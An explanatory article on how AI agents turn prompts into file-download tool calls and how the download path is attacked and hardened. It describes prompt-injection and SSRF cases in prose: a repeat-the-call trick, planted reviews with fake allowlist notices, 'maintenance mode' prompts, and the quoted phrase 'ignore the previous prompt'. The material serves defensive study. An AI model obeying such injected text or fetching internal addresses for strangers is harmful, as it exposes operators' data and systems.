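# File downloads by AI agents: how a prompt becomes a tool call, and how to keep the download path from being abused

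## What happens when an agent is asked to download a file

An AI agent is a program that lets a language model choose actions, carries those actions out, and feeds the results back to the model so it can choose again. The model only produces text and has no network connection or disk of its own. When someone tells an agent to download a file, the model writes structured text that names a function and its inputs. Ordinary software reads that text as a command, contacts a web server, and saves whatever comes back.

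This makes agents useful for fetching papers, spreadsheets and software. It also means that a web address can influence a program that has permissions on a machine, whether the user typed the address or a stranger planted it on a page the agent read. Most of the security problems with agent downloads arise because the text can come from people who were never given the permissions that the software uses.

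### The agent loop and the download tool

Many agents run in a cycle that researchers call ReAct, for reasoning and acting. The model writes some intermediate reasoning, emits a tool call, pauses for the tool's output, and uses that output to decide what to do next, according to *Silent Egress* (Lan, Kaul and colleagues, 2026), an eBay study of how web pages can make agents leak data. A tool is a function that software outside the model can run, and a tool call is the model's request to run it with given arguments.

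Ananto, Prevost-Avenel and colleagues (2026), in *ToFu*, a project that tests such tools for security bugs, write one turn of the cycle as a chain:

$$\text{input} \rightarrow M \rightarrow C \rightarrow H \rightarrow T \rightarrow \text{output}$$

Here M is the model, C is the call, T is the tool, and H is the orchestrator, the code that sits between the model and the tools. The call $C = \langle T, \{a_1 = v_1, \ldots, a_n = v_n\} \rangle$ consists of a tool's name and a value for each of its arguments. The orchestrator's parser finds the call in the model's text and turns it into a function name and arguments. Its executor then runs the function, and the output goes back to the model as new input.

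The model learns which tools exist from their schemas, machine-readable descriptions of each tool's name, arguments and types. A schema for a simple download tool could look like this:

```json
{
  "name": "download_file",
  "description": "Download a file and save it in the workspace",
  "inputSchema": {
    "type": "object",
    "properties": {
      "url": { "type": "string" },
      "destination": { "type": "string" }
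    },
    "required": ["url", "destination"]
  }
}
```

This layout follows the Model Context Protocol (MCP), a common standard for connecting agents to tool servers that other people wrote. In MCP's vocabulary, the host is the application in front of the user, a client inside the host communicates with a server, and the server offers the tools. Under the Model Context Protocol's *Tools* (2026) specification, the client requests the server's list of tools and later sends it a call with a tool name and arguments. MCP is now widely used. Anthropic's *Bringing MCP 2026-07-28 to Claude* (2026) reported more than 400 million monthly downloads of MCP's developer kits and over 950 servers in the directory of Claude, the company's assistant.

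The schema above enforces very little. Both arguments are strings, so it accepts any address and any file path. The word "workspace" (the folder in which an agent may read and write) appears in the description, which the model reads but no code enforces. MCP requires servers to validate all tool inputs, but many servers fall short. Ananto and colleagues tested 3,405 tools on 273 open-source MCP servers and verified bugs in 343 of the tools, on 118 servers. They conclude that a tool should treat every argument from a model as untrusted, even if it fits the schema.

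### One request, from the prompt to the disk

Suppose a company runs an agent on one of its servers and gives it the tool download_file(url, destination). An employee pastes a link to a PDF and writes, "Save this report and summarise it."

At this first stage, the employee writes the message, but the link in it may come from someone else, copied from an email or a search result. The model also receives the developer's standing instructions, earlier conversation, and pages the agent has already read. Lan and colleagues call this context flattening, because trusted instructions and untrusted web text share one window and the model has limited ability to rank them. Some assistants fetch a preview of any link in a message before the model does anything, which puts text written by the page's author into that window.

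The model then writes the tool call, copying the link into the `url` argument and making up a destination the employee never mentioned, such as `reports/annual-report.pdf`. Anyone whose text is in the context window can influence both values. The call is still only text, so nobody's privileges are in use yet.

Next the parser extracts the function name and the two arguments, and ordinary code handles the rest. This is the natural point for a person to intervene. The Model Context Protocol (MCP) specification recommends that a human always be able to deny a tool call. The MCP overview requires explicit consent for every tool but states that the protocol cannot enforce this. Whoever built the host therefore determines whether the employee sees a consent prompt.

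If the call goes ahead, the executor looks up the hostname in the link and opens a connection. Whoever chose the URL decides where that connection goes, but the request runs with the executor's privileges, which come from its position on the company network, its operating-system account, and any credentials it attaches.

The remote server may answer with a redirect, a response that sends the client to a different address. Whoever runs that server can therefore choose where the download comes from after the employee has approved the original link and after any check on it. HTTP clients commonly follow redirects automatically. *File Download Tools*, documentation from the Zitnik Lab at Harvard Medical School, describes a tool, also named download_file, that follows redirects by default.

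The executor then writes the file to disk. The remote server supplies the bytes and declares their type and length, while the model's tool call specifies the path. The executor's account permissions determine which folders it can write to and which existing files it could overwrite.

Finally, the agent opens the report to summarise it, and the text of the PDF enters the model's context window. Whoever wrote the PDF can now give the model instructions, just as the employee can, and the model can respond with any tool the agent has. From the first connection onward, the agent has used the privileges of the company that operates it to handle data that came mostly from strangers.

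### Confused deputies and injected instructions

Computer security calls this mismatch the confused deputy problem: someone who lacks certain privileges gets a program that has them to use them. The term goes back to a 1988 article by N. Hardy, which *Capability Gates Are Not Authorization* (2026) cites in its analysis of agent frameworks. In the standard example, a Fortran compiler had permission to write usage statistics into a protected directory. A user named the billing file, in that same directory, as the destination for debugging output, and the compiler overwrote the billing records.

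*Proof-of-Continuity* (2026) generalizes the compiler story into a definition involving a user U, a deputy D, and a privilege (o, r), meaning the right r over the object o. A confused deputy occurs when U lacks the privilege, D holds it, and D exercises it because of a request from U. The compiler's output file corresponds almost exactly to the destination argument of download_file. The url argument also fits the definition, with an internal web page as the object and reading it as the right.

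For an agent, U can be either the authenticated user or the author of a web page the agent fetches. *A Framework for Formalizing LLM Agent Security* (2026) describes the first case, in which an employee with no access to the personnel database asks for everyone's salary and the agent, which does have access, fetches the figures. With download_file, the equivalent would be an employee pasting a link to an internal page that their own account cannot open. Lan and colleagues describe the second case, in which the agent cannot reliably tell the user's request to fetch a page from instructions inside the page. Running the tool with the user's own permissions fixes the salary case. It does much less against the web page's author, because the user may well have permission for an action they never asked for.

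Prompt injection is text that makes a model follow an attacker's instructions. In direct injection, the attacker types the text into the prompt. Tsigkopoulos and Ntantogian (2026), in *From Prompt Injection to Web Exploitation*, credit Perez and Ribeiro with the first demonstration, in which a line such as "ignore the previous prompt" overrode the developer's instructions. In indirect injection, which Greshake and colleagues described in 2023, the instructions are in content that the agent retrieves, such as a web page, an email or a downloaded PDF.

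There is no reliable way yet to make a model ignore such text. In *Prompt injection is not SQL injection*, Britain's National Cyber Security Centre (NCSC) lists current approaches, such as training models to put instructions ahead of anything in the data, and points out that they all impose a distinction between instructions and data on a technology that doesn't have one. It prefers to think of the model as an "inherently confusable deputy". SQL injection attacks slip database commands into a web form, and programmers learned to prevent them by keeping commands and data apart. The NCSC thinks prompt injection may never have so complete a remedy, according to ITPro's *NCSC issues urgent warning over growing AI prompt injection risks*.

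According to *Authorization Architectures for Tool-Using AI Agents* (2026), an agent differs from the old compiler in that the model's decision depends on the prompt and is probabilistic, authority is spread over users, operators, sub-agents and services, and the hostile request arrives inside a document. The probabilistic behaviour matters most for testing, because a model that refused a malicious instruction yesterday may follow it today, whereas a compiler with this flaw makes the same mistake every time. That is a reason to put the checks in the tool. Tsigkopoulos and Ntantogian note that the model usually does not create the underlying vulnerability but carries the attacker's influence to a component that trusts the model's output too much.

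### How this differs from a download in a browser

When a person clicks a download link, they send the request from their own device, see the file arrive, and decide whether to open it, but each of these steps changes when an agent downloads the file instead.

The request may come from a server inside a private network, where it can reach machines that the public internet cannot. Vendors are making this setup easier. Anthropic, for example, has released a research preview of tunnels that connect Claude to MCP servers inside a company's network without a public endpoint or inbound firewall rule. A download tool on one of those servers would send its requests from inside the network. A browser on an office laptop does too, but it normally stops one website from reading what another returns, while a bare HTTP client has no such restriction.

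Often nobody inspects the file or the steps around it. Lan and colleagues had an agent summarise hostile web pages 480 times. The agent sent out sensitive data in about 89% of the runs, and 95% of the successful attacks got past checks that examined only the final answer. The 89% figure will not carry over to other agents, because the model was small (qwen2.5:7b) and the researchers had placed the secrets directly in its context. The 95% figure is more general, because a check on the final answer does not cover network requests, whichever model makes them.

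The agent may also act on the file straight away. In 2023 the security firm Positive Security attacked AutoGPT, an early AI agent. *Hacking Auto-GPT and escaping its docker container* (2023) reports that once the agent had written a Python script to disk, it very reliably ran the script next, without being told to. Explicit instructions to write the file and then run it worked less well, because the agent often tried to run the file before writing it.

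### AutoGPT's download command

AutoGPT popularised the loop that most agents still use. It took a goal from the user and prompted a model, usually GPT-4 or GPT-3.5, to reply in a fixed JSON format with its reasoning and the next command. It then ran the command and added the output to the conversation. By default the user had to approve each command, but in "continuous mode" the program ran commands without waiting for approval. Version 0.4.2 had twenty commands enabled by default, but download_file was not among them and users had to enable it in the settings.

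The code for this command is short and checks one of its two arguments, the filename. AutoGPT first passed the filename to a helper function. AutoGPT's workspace module shows that the helper joined the name to the workspace folder, resolved the result to an absolute path, and raised an error if that path lay outside the folder. The check ran only while the RESTRICT_TO_WORKSPACE setting was on, which was the default according to AutoGPT's settings template.

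The URL got no comparable treatment. The command passed it directly to requests, a Python library for HTTP, with redirects explicitly allowed, and never checked the host or its network address. It set no timeout, so a server that accepted the connection and then sent nothing could keep the command waiting indefinitely. It wrote data to disk in pieces of 8,192 bytes for as long as the server kept sending. The code read Content-Length, the header in which a server declares a file's size, but used it only for the progress display and the success message. A server that omitted the header could send data until the disk was full. If it stopped before then, the command would tell the agent that it had successfully downloaded a file of size zero.

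A current tool, Charmbracelet's *download.go* in the coding agent Crush, makes nearly the opposite choices. It requests permission before it connects and includes both the URL and the full path in the request. It cuts the transfer off at 100 MB whatever size the server declared, and its default client times out after five minutes. But it accepts an absolute path to anywhere on the disk, relying on the permission step to catch a bad one, and it checks only that the URL begins with http or https. It sets no redirect rule, so the standard client in Go, the language it is written in, follows up to ten redirects. The user can therefore approve one address and receive a file from another. Neither program's code checks where an address actually leads.

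MCP has no standard method for file transfers yet. *Exploring File Uploads and Downloads in MCP* (Model Context Protocol, 2026) presents a draft that would keep both the download address and the file's bytes away from the model, which would see only a line such as "Exported q3-orders.csv." The client would have to refuse redirects, discard any file whose size does not match the declared one, and treat even a matching file as untrusted. The draft covers files that a tool server produces, so a link that a user pastes from the open web would still go through tools like the two above.

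Flaws in agent software usually become public through security advisories, which describe the flaw and typically name the affected versions and the fix. Many advisories carry a CVE number, which identifies the flaw in a shared public catalogue of vulnerabilities. Positive Security's work led to several, including CVE-2023-37275, which covers a way to fake system messages on AutoGPT's console in versions before 0.4.3. GitLab's *AGiXT Vulnerable to Path Traversal in safe_join()* (2026) describes a function in another agent package that failed to confirm that file paths stayed inside the workspace. AutoGPT had a function with almost the same name for the same check three years earlier.

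### What an attacker can gain

One kind of harm is unauthorized access. In an attack known as server-side request forgery, the agent's server sends a request to an internal address on behalf of someone who could not connect to it directly.

A download can also cause data to be lost or corrupted. If the agent requests a URL that contains secrets, whoever runs the receiving server can read them. Writing to the wrong path can destroy an existing file, and a saved file can contain code or instructions that the agent later acts on.

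The remaining kind is resource exhaustion, which can be caused by a file that never ends, an archive that expands to fill the disk, or a loop of downloads that runs up a bill.

All of these have counterparts in the 2026 list of top risks for language-model applications from OWASP, a non-profit that publishes software-security guidance. According to SC Media's *OWASP updates Top 10 security risks for LLM applications*, the list ranks prompt injection first, ahead of sensitive information disclosure and excessive agency, and "unbounded consumption" lower. The ranking reflects practitioners' judgement more than the number of attacks. Infosecurity Magazine's *Prompt Injection Remains Biggest LLM Risk, Despite Limited Incidents* reports that prompt injection has led the list for three years running even though recorded incidents remain relatively few.

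## How model output is turned into a tool call

*Your model isn't bad at tool calling. Your serving stack is* (Wilson, 2026), a guide from the voice-agent company LiveKit, splits the path from a model's output to a running function into three parts. The model writes a call in the syntax it learned during training. The serving stack, which hosts the model, translates that syntax into a structured field. The agent framework reads the field and runs the function. Different organisations often write these parts, and several of the faults below come from the gaps between them.

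### From the schema to the function

Before the model produces anything, a chat template turns the list of messages and tools into one stretch of text, in the layout the model saw during training. The tool schemas go into that text too. OpenAI's *Function calling* guide confirms this for the company's hosted models: the server puts the functions into the system message, where they take up context and cost the developer input tokens. For the employee who wants a report saved, a simplified prompt, without the markers that real templates put between the parts, could look like this:

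```
You can call the following tool.
{"name": "download_file",
 "description": "Download a file and save it in the workspace",
 "parameters": {"url": "string", "destination": "string"}}

Save this report and summarise it.
https://files.example.com/annual-report.pdf
```

The model continues this text one token (a short piece of text from its vocabulary) at a time. If its training covered tool use, a likely continuation is a call:

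```
{"name": "download_file",
 "arguments": {"url": "https://files.example.com/annual-report.pdf",
               "destination": "reports/annual-report.pdf"}}
```

The serving stack's parser finds the call in the output and moves it into a field named `tool_calls`. In OpenAI's Chat Completions interface, which many other providers copy, the arguments arrive as JSON text inside a string, so the inner quotation marks carry backslashes:

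```json
{
  "id": "call_1",
  "type": "function",
  "function": {
    "name": "download_file",
    "arguments": "{\"url\": \"https://files.example.com/annual-report.pdf\", \"destination\": \"reports/annual-report.pdf\"}"
  }
}
```

The framework looks up the name among its registered functions, decodes the string, usually checks the types against the schema, and runs the function:

```python
download_file(
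    url="https://files.example.com/annual-report.pdf",
    destination="reports/annual-report.pdf",
)
```

It then sends the result back with the call's `id` so the model can match each result to its call. One reply can contain several calls, and OpenAI advises developers to assume it will. Liquid AI, which makes small models for phones and laptops, recommends returning an error message as the tool's result if the tool name is unknown or the arguments are malformed, so that the loop can continue.

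### Formats for the call

The syntax in the second step varies a good deal between models and frameworks.

| Format | What the model writes | How software finds the call |
|---|---|---|
| ReAct text | A line beginning "Action:" with the tool's name, then a line beginning "Action Input:" with the arguments | Searches for the two labels |
| AutoGPT's JSON reply | One JSON object that holds both the reasoning and the next command | Decodes the whole reply |
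| Tagged JSON | Free text, with a JSON object between an opening and a closing tag | Searches for the tags and decodes what lies between them |
| Special tokens | Reserved vocabulary items around the name and arguments | Looks for those items in the token stream |
| API field | Any of the above, which the server has already translated | Reads `tool_calls` and decodes the argument string |

The ReAct pattern needs no special training, only a model that follows instructions, and it can still work well. In *Interface-Induced Trajectory Censoring*, Wang and Sang (2026) gave a 7-billion-parameter coding model 100 programming problems and one tool for running tests. Software could parse a call on 95 of the problems with a ReAct-style text format, compared with 84 with a correctly configured function-calling interface. The drawback is that "Action:" is ordinary text, so it can also appear in a page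 that the model quotes.

AutoGPT's command list, which Positive Security reproduced, gave each command a name, a short description and a placeholder for each argument, but no separate type information. Because the entire reply had to be JSON, a sentence before the opening brace would make it invalid. Tags avoid this problem by letting the model write prose around the call.

Some models, including Google's Gemma 4 and Moonshot AI's Kimi K2, mark their tool calls with special tokens, each of which is a single entry in the vocabulary. If a user types a copy of a special token, a careful server encodes it as ordinary characters, so quoted text is less likely to look like a call. This does not protect against a model that generates the special token itself because something in its context led it to.

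Some models write the call as a line of Python, such as `download_file(url="...", destination="...")`. According to *Tool Calling*, part of the documentation for the widely used open-source serving engine vLLM, developers have not agreed on which tokens should open and close such a call. The Llama 3.2 models emit none, so the parser has to recognize a call from the format of the text alone. The documentation lists more than twenty parser settings, each for a particular family of models, and the right setting can change from one generation to the next. For example, Liquid AI switched from Python-style calls to XML in its newest models.

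### Constrained decoding

A server can also prevent malformed calls while the model is writing them. At each step the model gives every token $i$ in its vocabulary a score $z_i$, and the server normally converts all the scores into probabilities. In constrained decoding, a grammar engine keeps track of the text $s$ written so far and works out $A(s)$, the set of tokens that could still lead to a valid call. It then masks the rest:

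$$p(i \mid s) = \begin{cases} \dfrac{e^{z_i}}{\sum_{j \in A(s)} e^{z_j}} & \text{if } i \in A(s) \\[2ex] 0 & \text{otherwise} \end{cases}$$

Suppose the model has just written `"url":`. The schema requires a string, so the mask leaves only tokens that can begin one, and a number or a bracket has probability zero. Once the string has opened, nearly every character is legal, so an address on the company's private network fits the grammar as well as the link to the annual report does.

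The guarantee therefore covers only the form of the call. vLLM guarantees a "validly-parsable function call - not a high-quality one", provided the reply doesn't hit its length limit partway through the JSON. The arguments will have the declared names and types, but the grammar can't determine whether the URL is safe to fetch.

An agent's model must be able to answer in prose as well as call tools, and serving engines handle this with structural tags. *Structural Tag Usage*, from the documentation of the constrained-decoding library XGrammar, describes these tags as a way to mix free text with structured fragments, including each model's own wrapper for tool calls. The model generates text freely until it opens a tool call, and the grammar applies from that point.

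Whether vLLM enforces a tool's schema depends on the request's `tool_choice` setting. If the developer names a function or sets `required`, vLLM always constrains the arguments. With `auto`, the usual setting for an agent, the model decides whether to call a tool. According to its current documentation, vLLM then enforces the schema only if at least one tool sets `strict: true`, the selected parser supports structural tags, and the operator has not turned off a server-wide switch that is on by default. Otherwise the model generates text without constraints, the parser extracts the call from that text, and the arguments may be malformed or violate the schema.

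According to an older version of vLLM's *Tool Calling* page, earlier releases accepted the `strict` field to avoid breaking clients that sent it, but ignored it. A developer who upgrades an application without upgrading the server could easily assume, wrongly, that the server enforces `strict`.

OpenAI recommends always using its strict mode, which requires the schema to set `additionalProperties: false` on every object and list every field as required, with `null` as an allowed type for optional ones. If a developer sets `strict: true` on a schema that breaks these rules, the server rejects the request. If the developer omits `strict`, the newer Responses interface tries to convert the schema and falls back to best-effort calling when it can't, while the older Chat Completions interface defaults to non-strict mode.

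Strict mode can stop a model from calling the wrong function. Wang and Sang found that on 22 of 100 programming problems, even with the official template, Llama-3.1-8B called the function named in the problem instead of the test tool it had been given. Better instructions to the model did not fix the mistake. Adding `strict: true` cut the number to zero, and the number of problems solved rose from 44 to 61. But strict mode does not determine whether a call should happen at all, as *Strict tool calling*, the documentation for another serving engine, mistral.rs, explains.

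### When the parser gets it wrong

A tool call is missed when the parser doesn't recognise what the model wrote and the framework receives it as ordinary text. Wilson describes voice agents that read the call aloud to a customer. The same model weights can work behind one provider and fail behind another.

Wang and Sang measured how large the effect can be by running Qwen2.5-Coder-7B on part of the Berkeley Function Calling Leaderboard. With the template and parser that the documentation recommended for the wider Qwen2.5 family, the official score on simple Python calls was 0.00. With a template and parser made for that model, it was 0.96. Across 200 first requests, replacing only the template or only the parser recovered no calls, while replacing both recovered 196. The parser had no bug, since it correctly rejected text outside its own format, but nobody had checked that the two components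 matched.

These failures are easy to misread because the server reports success and returns an empty `tool_calls` field, just as it does when the model doesn't attempt a call. A security tester who plants a malicious download link and sees no call may conclude that the model didn't try to download the file, when the parser actually dropped the call. The same model might start downloading after the next server upgrade, so testers also need to read the raw output.

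vLLM's *Chasing 100% Accuracy* traces a similar case through several layers. In a test of about 4,000 requests, Moonshot AI's own service produced 1,286 valid calls from Kimi K2, while vLLM 0.11.0 produced 218. Most of the losses came from a template parameter that vLLM did not pass on, so the prompt stopped before the marker that opens the assistant's turn. The template also mishandled empty messages, and the parser threw away whole calls when their ID lacked an expected full stop. Repairs brought the total to around 1,000. More than 300 other calls still failed validation, and in some of them the model had named a tool from earlier in the conversation that the current request did not offer. A framework must therefore refuse any name outside the current list, however well formed the call is.

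Parsers can also deliver the wrong arguments. Red Hat, whose engineers work on vLLM, warns that a parser that expects the label "arguments" may pass on empty arguments when the model writes "parameters". Another parser may keep only the first of several calls, or take values from the model's reasoning. The last error could make download_file fetch a link that the model had rejected in its reasoning.

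Many servers send the output in pieces while the model is still writing, which can corrupt tool calls. The *Laguna M.1/XS.2 Technical Report* (2026) describes open-source parsers that could emit invalid calls when a piece contained more than one token. *FailureAtlas* (2026), a catalogue of faults in model-serving software, records a proxy that restarted its call counter with every piece, which merged several parallel calls into one corrupted JSON string.

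If the stream stops early, some parsers fill in the missing end of the call. In *Oops!... I Parsed It Again*, Santos-Grueiro and Romero-Ruiz (2026) cut off a call in the middle of the number 12. The partial parser in LangChain, a popular agent framework, closed the object and returned 1 instead of 12. Python's strict parser and two Go decoders rejected the fragment. The same kind of error in a URL would be hard to spot, because a truncated URL is often still a valid link to something else. Liquid AI advises collecting the fragments of each call separately and parsing them only once the server reports that the model finished with a tool call. A call that ended for any other reason should be discarded.

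**Ordinary text mistaken for a call.** Developers often respond to missed calls by making the parser more lenient. *PDE-Agents* (2026), a system for running engineering simulations, uses a model that writes its calls as plain text. Its parser first tries to read the whole reply as JSON, then looks inside code blocks, then takes the first passage in curly brackets, and finally tries to repair truncated JSON by closing the brackets. This recovers real calls, but it also lets more kinds of text trigger a tool. If a user asks how download_file works and the model answers with an example, a parser this lenient could run the example. LiveKit's framework avoids this by reading calls only from the structured field, but it fails whenever the server's parser fails.

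### The Repeat-After-Me demonstration

An attacker can cause the same confusion on purpose. Ananto and colleagues demonstrated this with what they call the Repeat-After-Me attack. They wrote out a tool call in the format that a framework recognises and asked the model to repeat it word for word. The framework treated the model's copy as a call and ran the tool with the attacker's arguments. They reproduced the attack on six frameworks: LangGraph, Microsoft Agent Framework, Google's ADK 2.0, AutoGen, Strands and CrewAI.

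The researchers published a full transcript for LangGraph, using the small model llama3.1:8b and two harmless dummy tools with alarming names. The system prompt told the model to decline anything dangerous. The model first refused, but quoted the requested call in its refusal. The parser did not treat the quotation as a call, so nothing ran. The researchers then asked for only the quoted text. LangGraph received a structured call with exactly the arguments they had supplied and ran the tool immediately. The model refused only after the tool had returned its result.

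The transcript covers one fairly weak model, and Ananto and colleagues give no success rates for the six frameworks, so the demonstration is little evidence of how often a stronger model would comply. The person typing was also the agent's user, who may have been entitled to use the tools anyway. A web page that persuades the model to repeat a call would be more worrying. But the LangGraph framework didn't check whether a call should run between parsing it and running it, and a better model wouldn't add that check. The researchers reported the missing check to LangGraph's maintainers.

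A valid call therefore shows only that the model produced text in the right format, not that anyone authorised the call. The call's `id` doesn't help, since it only links a result to a request. To decide whether a download is authorised, the code that runs the tool needs information from outside the call, such as which user is logged in and what that user's policy allows.

### Parse once

A good policy check can still fail if the call it checks differs from the call that runs. This can happen when components parse the same call separately and interpret it differently. Santos-Grueiro and Romero-Ruiz found such differences for most pairs among 17 parser and validator configurations.

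The remedy is to parse the arguments once, keep only the fields that the approved schema declares, and pass the resulting object to both the check and the executor. In outline:

```python
parsed = parse_arguments(raw_text)       # the only place that reads the text
call = keep_declared_fields(parsed, approved_schema)

if policy_allows(user, "download_file", call):
    download_file(**call)
```

Nothing after the first line should go back to `raw_text`. The audit log should record `call`, and if a person has to approve the download, the prompt should display `call` too. `call` must not change between the check and the download. The same rule applies to any JSON text inside an argument, which developers may be tempted to parse again later. *PDE-Agents* gave every tool a helper function to unwrap arguments because its model sometimes encoded them twice. Under the parse-once rule, that unwrapping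 belongs in the first line, before the check.

When the check and the executor run on different machines, the call must be sent over the network as bytes again. Santos-Grueiro and Romero-Ruiz seal the parsed call together with its ID so the receiver can detect any change made in transit. Their full design stopped all 7,412 of their crafted inputs and every attack they built. They also tried stricter validation, a comparison of two parsers, and a single check that forwarded the original bytes. An attacker who knew which of these was in use could defeat it. The result is strong evidence for giving the executor the parsed call itself, although the same researchers built both the attacks and the defence.

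The rule keeps the approved call and the executed call identical. It does nothing about a policy that approves a bad URL.

### A stricter schema for download_file

The schema in the previous section accepted any two strings. A tighter version, in OpenAI's layout, could look like this:

```json
{
  "type": "function",
  "name": "download_file",
  "description": "Download one file that the user asked for",
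  "strict": true,
  "parameters": {
    "type": "object",
    "properties": {
      "url": {
        "type": "string",
        "pattern": "^https://[^\\s]+$",
        "description": "Full https link to the file"
      },
      "destination": {
        "type": "string",
        "enum": ["reports", "data"],
        "description": "Folder in the workspace"
      }
    },
    "required": ["url", "destination"],
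    "additionalProperties": false
  }
}
```

The biggest change is to `destination`, where the model used to write a whole path and now picks one of two folders, while ordinary code chooses the file name. This follows OpenAI's advice to use fixed lists of values so that invalid requests can't be expressed, and to avoid asking the model for anything the program already knows. The `url` field now excludes plain http links and other schemes, such as those that open local files. Extra fields are no longer valid.

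The executor should check the parsed call against this schema again before it acts, because the server may have fallen back to best-effort parsing. Strict modes also do not support every JSON Schema feature, so a `pattern` that works on one server may cause an error on another. OpenAI also lets developers write a grammar for a tool's input, which could restrict the URL to a few named hosts, but a grammar constrains only what the model writes, not the connection that follows.

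Checking the URL against the schema leaves most of its risk in place. A link that matches the pattern can still lead or redirect to a machine inside the company's network, or send confidential data out in its query string. The schema does not limit the size or number of downloads, and it cannot detect harmful file contents. A call induced by a hostile web page would pass the check as easily as one the employee requested.

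## How an attacker's URL reaches the download tool

A valid call to download_file doesn't show who chose the URL. What an attacker needs depends on where the URL came from. Harm depends on whether the model copies the URL into a call, and then on whether the tool checks it.

### Where the URL comes from

| Source of the URL | What the attacker needs | Must the attacker trick the model? |
|---|---|---|
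| A malicious user types it | Access to the chat, and an agent that can reach something the attacker can't | Only if the model's instructions or training lead it to refuse |
| An honest user pastes it | A link that the user thinks is worth downloading | No |
| The agent reads it in a page, a file or an earlier tool result | A place to put text that the agent will read | Usually |
| It arrives in submitted chat history | An application that accepts past messages from the user's device | Usually |
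| The model invents it | Control of an address that the model happens to make up | No |

Malicious users matter mainly for agents that run on somebody else's server. A person who runs an agent on their own laptop gains little by tricking it into opening an address, because they could open it themselves. But when a public chatbot runs inside a company's network, any user may be able to make it open internal addresses that can't be reached from outside.

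An attacker's link is hardest for a model to catch when an honest user pastes it, because the user has asked for the download and there is no injected instruction to resist. A model that resists every known injection could still download a report from a link that the user copied from a phishing email.

If the agent takes URLs from content it reads, an attacker can plant one in a product review, a shared document or a public code repository. Tsigkopoulos and Ntantogian describe a flaw that security researchers at Snyk Labs found in a tool server for Amazon's cloud. A poisoned file in a repository could lead a coding assistant to add the attacker's command to its calls to that server, even if the attacker couldn't contact the server directly. An attacker doesn't always need to plant an instruction. If a user asks an agent to collect every spreadsheet linked from a page, it will fetch whatever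 the page's author linked.

Chat history is an easily overlooked route for an attacker's URL. A model keeps no memory between requests, so the application sends it the earlier conversation with each new message. If the user's browser holds that transcript, the user can edit it before sending, for example by adding a tool result that never existed or a reply in which the assistant agreed to fetch an address. Storing the transcript on the server prevents this. Long-term memory is a similar route. Tsigkopoulos and Ntantogian sketch but do not test a scenario in which a malicious page makes a logged-in victim's browser save a false entry in an agent's memory. The entry could stay unused until it affects an unrelated conversation.

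Models also fill in URLs nobody gave them. Ananto and colleagues ran VIPER-MCP, a rival security tester that uses a model to try to exploit tools. On one server whose URL fetching had a real flaw, the model called the tool with a placeholder address on example.com, so the tester did not confirm the flaw. That domain is harmless because internet authorities reserve it for documentation. An invented address on an ordinary domain could belong to anyone, including an attacker who has noticed that models tend to produce it.

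### The TicketOracle experiment

To see how often models pass a hostile URL to a tool, Tsigkopoulos and Ntantogian built TicketOracle, a small web application with a chatbot that answers questions about concerts. The model has one tool, fetch_event_data, which takes a URL, sends a GET request (the ordinary request for reading a page) and returns the response, cut to a fixed length. It works like a download tool that doesn't save anything, and its code doesn't restrict the URL.

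The same machine runs an administrative interface that holds user records and can delete users and events. It listens only on the loopback address, which a computer uses to contact itself. Outsiders therefore can't connect to it, but the tool can because it runs on that machine.

The attacker in the experiment has no password and can do only two things: write to the chatbot and post text about an event, such as a review. The attacker knows that the chatbot can fetch URLs and guesses common administrative paths. The attacker always supplies the full URL, so the model never has to work out an internal address for itself. There were five scenarios:

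- **Port probing.** The attacker asks the chatbot to contact a port on the server and infers from the reply whether a service is running there.
- **Data leak.** The attacker has it fetch the list of users, with their addresses and phone numbers.
- **State change.** The attacker has it open a URL that deletes a user or an event.
- **Blind request.** The URL has the same kind of effect but returns an empty response, so the attacker can't see whether it worked.
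- **Planted review.** The attacker hides an instruction in a review, and the agent reads it when an innocent user asks about the concert.

The researchers ran each scenario ten times on each of seven models in April 2026. The table gives the number of successful attacks out of ten. In the last column, the system prompt (the developer's standing instructions) also contained an allowlist of permitted URLs.

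| Model | Port probing | Data leak | State change | Blind request | Planted review | Planted review, with allowlist |
|---|---|---|---|---|---|---|
| Llama 3.3 70B | 10 | 10 | 10 | 10 | 6 | 10 |
| DeepSeek R1 | 10 | 10 | 10 | 7 | 0 | 0 |
| Qwen3 Coder 480B | 9 | 10 | 10 | 7 | 0 | 0 |
| Gemini 3 Pro Preview | 0 | 7 | 10 | 0 | 0 | 0 |
| GPT-oss 120B | 3 | 0 | 10 | 0 | 5 | 0 |
| GPT-5.2 | 0 | 0 | 0 | 0 | 0 | 0 |
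| Claude Opus 4.6 | 0 | 0 | 0 | 0 | 0 | 0 |

The same application's vulnerability therefore depended on the model. Llama complied with all forty direct attacks, while no attack counted as successful with GPT-5.2 or Claude Opus 4.6. Except for blind requests, which the researchers checked in a server log, an attack counted only if the agent both made the request and repeated the result to the user. An agent that fetched the user list without reporting it would still score zero. The researchers state that Claude never ran the fetch in any trial. They don't state this for GPT-5.2, although its blind requests never reached the server.

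The refusals did not match how much damage each request could do. Gemini refused to probe a port but carried out the state-changing request ten times out of ten. It refused every blind request, even though those would have had the same effect on the server as the state-changing request. The state changes worked because the administrative interface accepted them through GET requests, so even a tool meant only for reading pages could destroy data.

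### An allowlist in the system prompt

The second version of TicketOracle listed the permitted URL patterns and event names in the system prompt and told the model to refuse anything else. These few lines of instructions stopped all four direct attacks on all seven models, including Llama, even though the tool's code still accepted any address.

The instruction did not reliably stop the attack in the planted review. The attack succeeded against Llama 10 times out of 10, up from 6, while its successes against GPT-oss fell from 5 to 0 and the other five models stayed at 0. The review contained a fake notice that the allowlist now included the internal address, and Llama treated the notice as genuine every time. Tsigkopoulos and Ntantogian conclude that instructions of this kind are a guardrail and should not be the main security boundary.

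Llama's ten successes support that conclusion, but they are weak evidence that the allowlist made Llama more vulnerable. The researchers added the text about the allowlist when they tested the second version, so the attack changed along with the defence. The samples are also small. If Llama had been equally vulnerable in both versions, a gap at least as wide as 6 against 10 would occur by chance about 9% of the time, even if the trials were independent.

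The trials were not independent either, because each set of ten ran within one conversation and the model could see its earlier answers. Claude's refusals to probe ports, for instance, began as long explanations and ended as little more than single words. A score of 10 or 0 may therefore reflect one early decision that the model kept repeating.

The attacks were also simple. One told the model that it was in a maintenance mode with full access, and the researchers did not refine their prompts when a model refused. A zero means that a model resisted these prompts, but a more persistent attacker might have succeeded.

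### Injection results on newer models

Claude Opus 4.6 was much more vulnerable to injection attacks when operating a graphical interface than when working in a constrained coding environment. VentureBeat reports, from the model's system card (the developer's account of its safety tests), that all 200 attempts failed in the coding environment. In the graphical interface, a single attempt succeeded 17.8% of the time without extra safeguards. Within 200 attempts, at least one succeeded 78.6% of the time without the safeguards and 57.1% with them.

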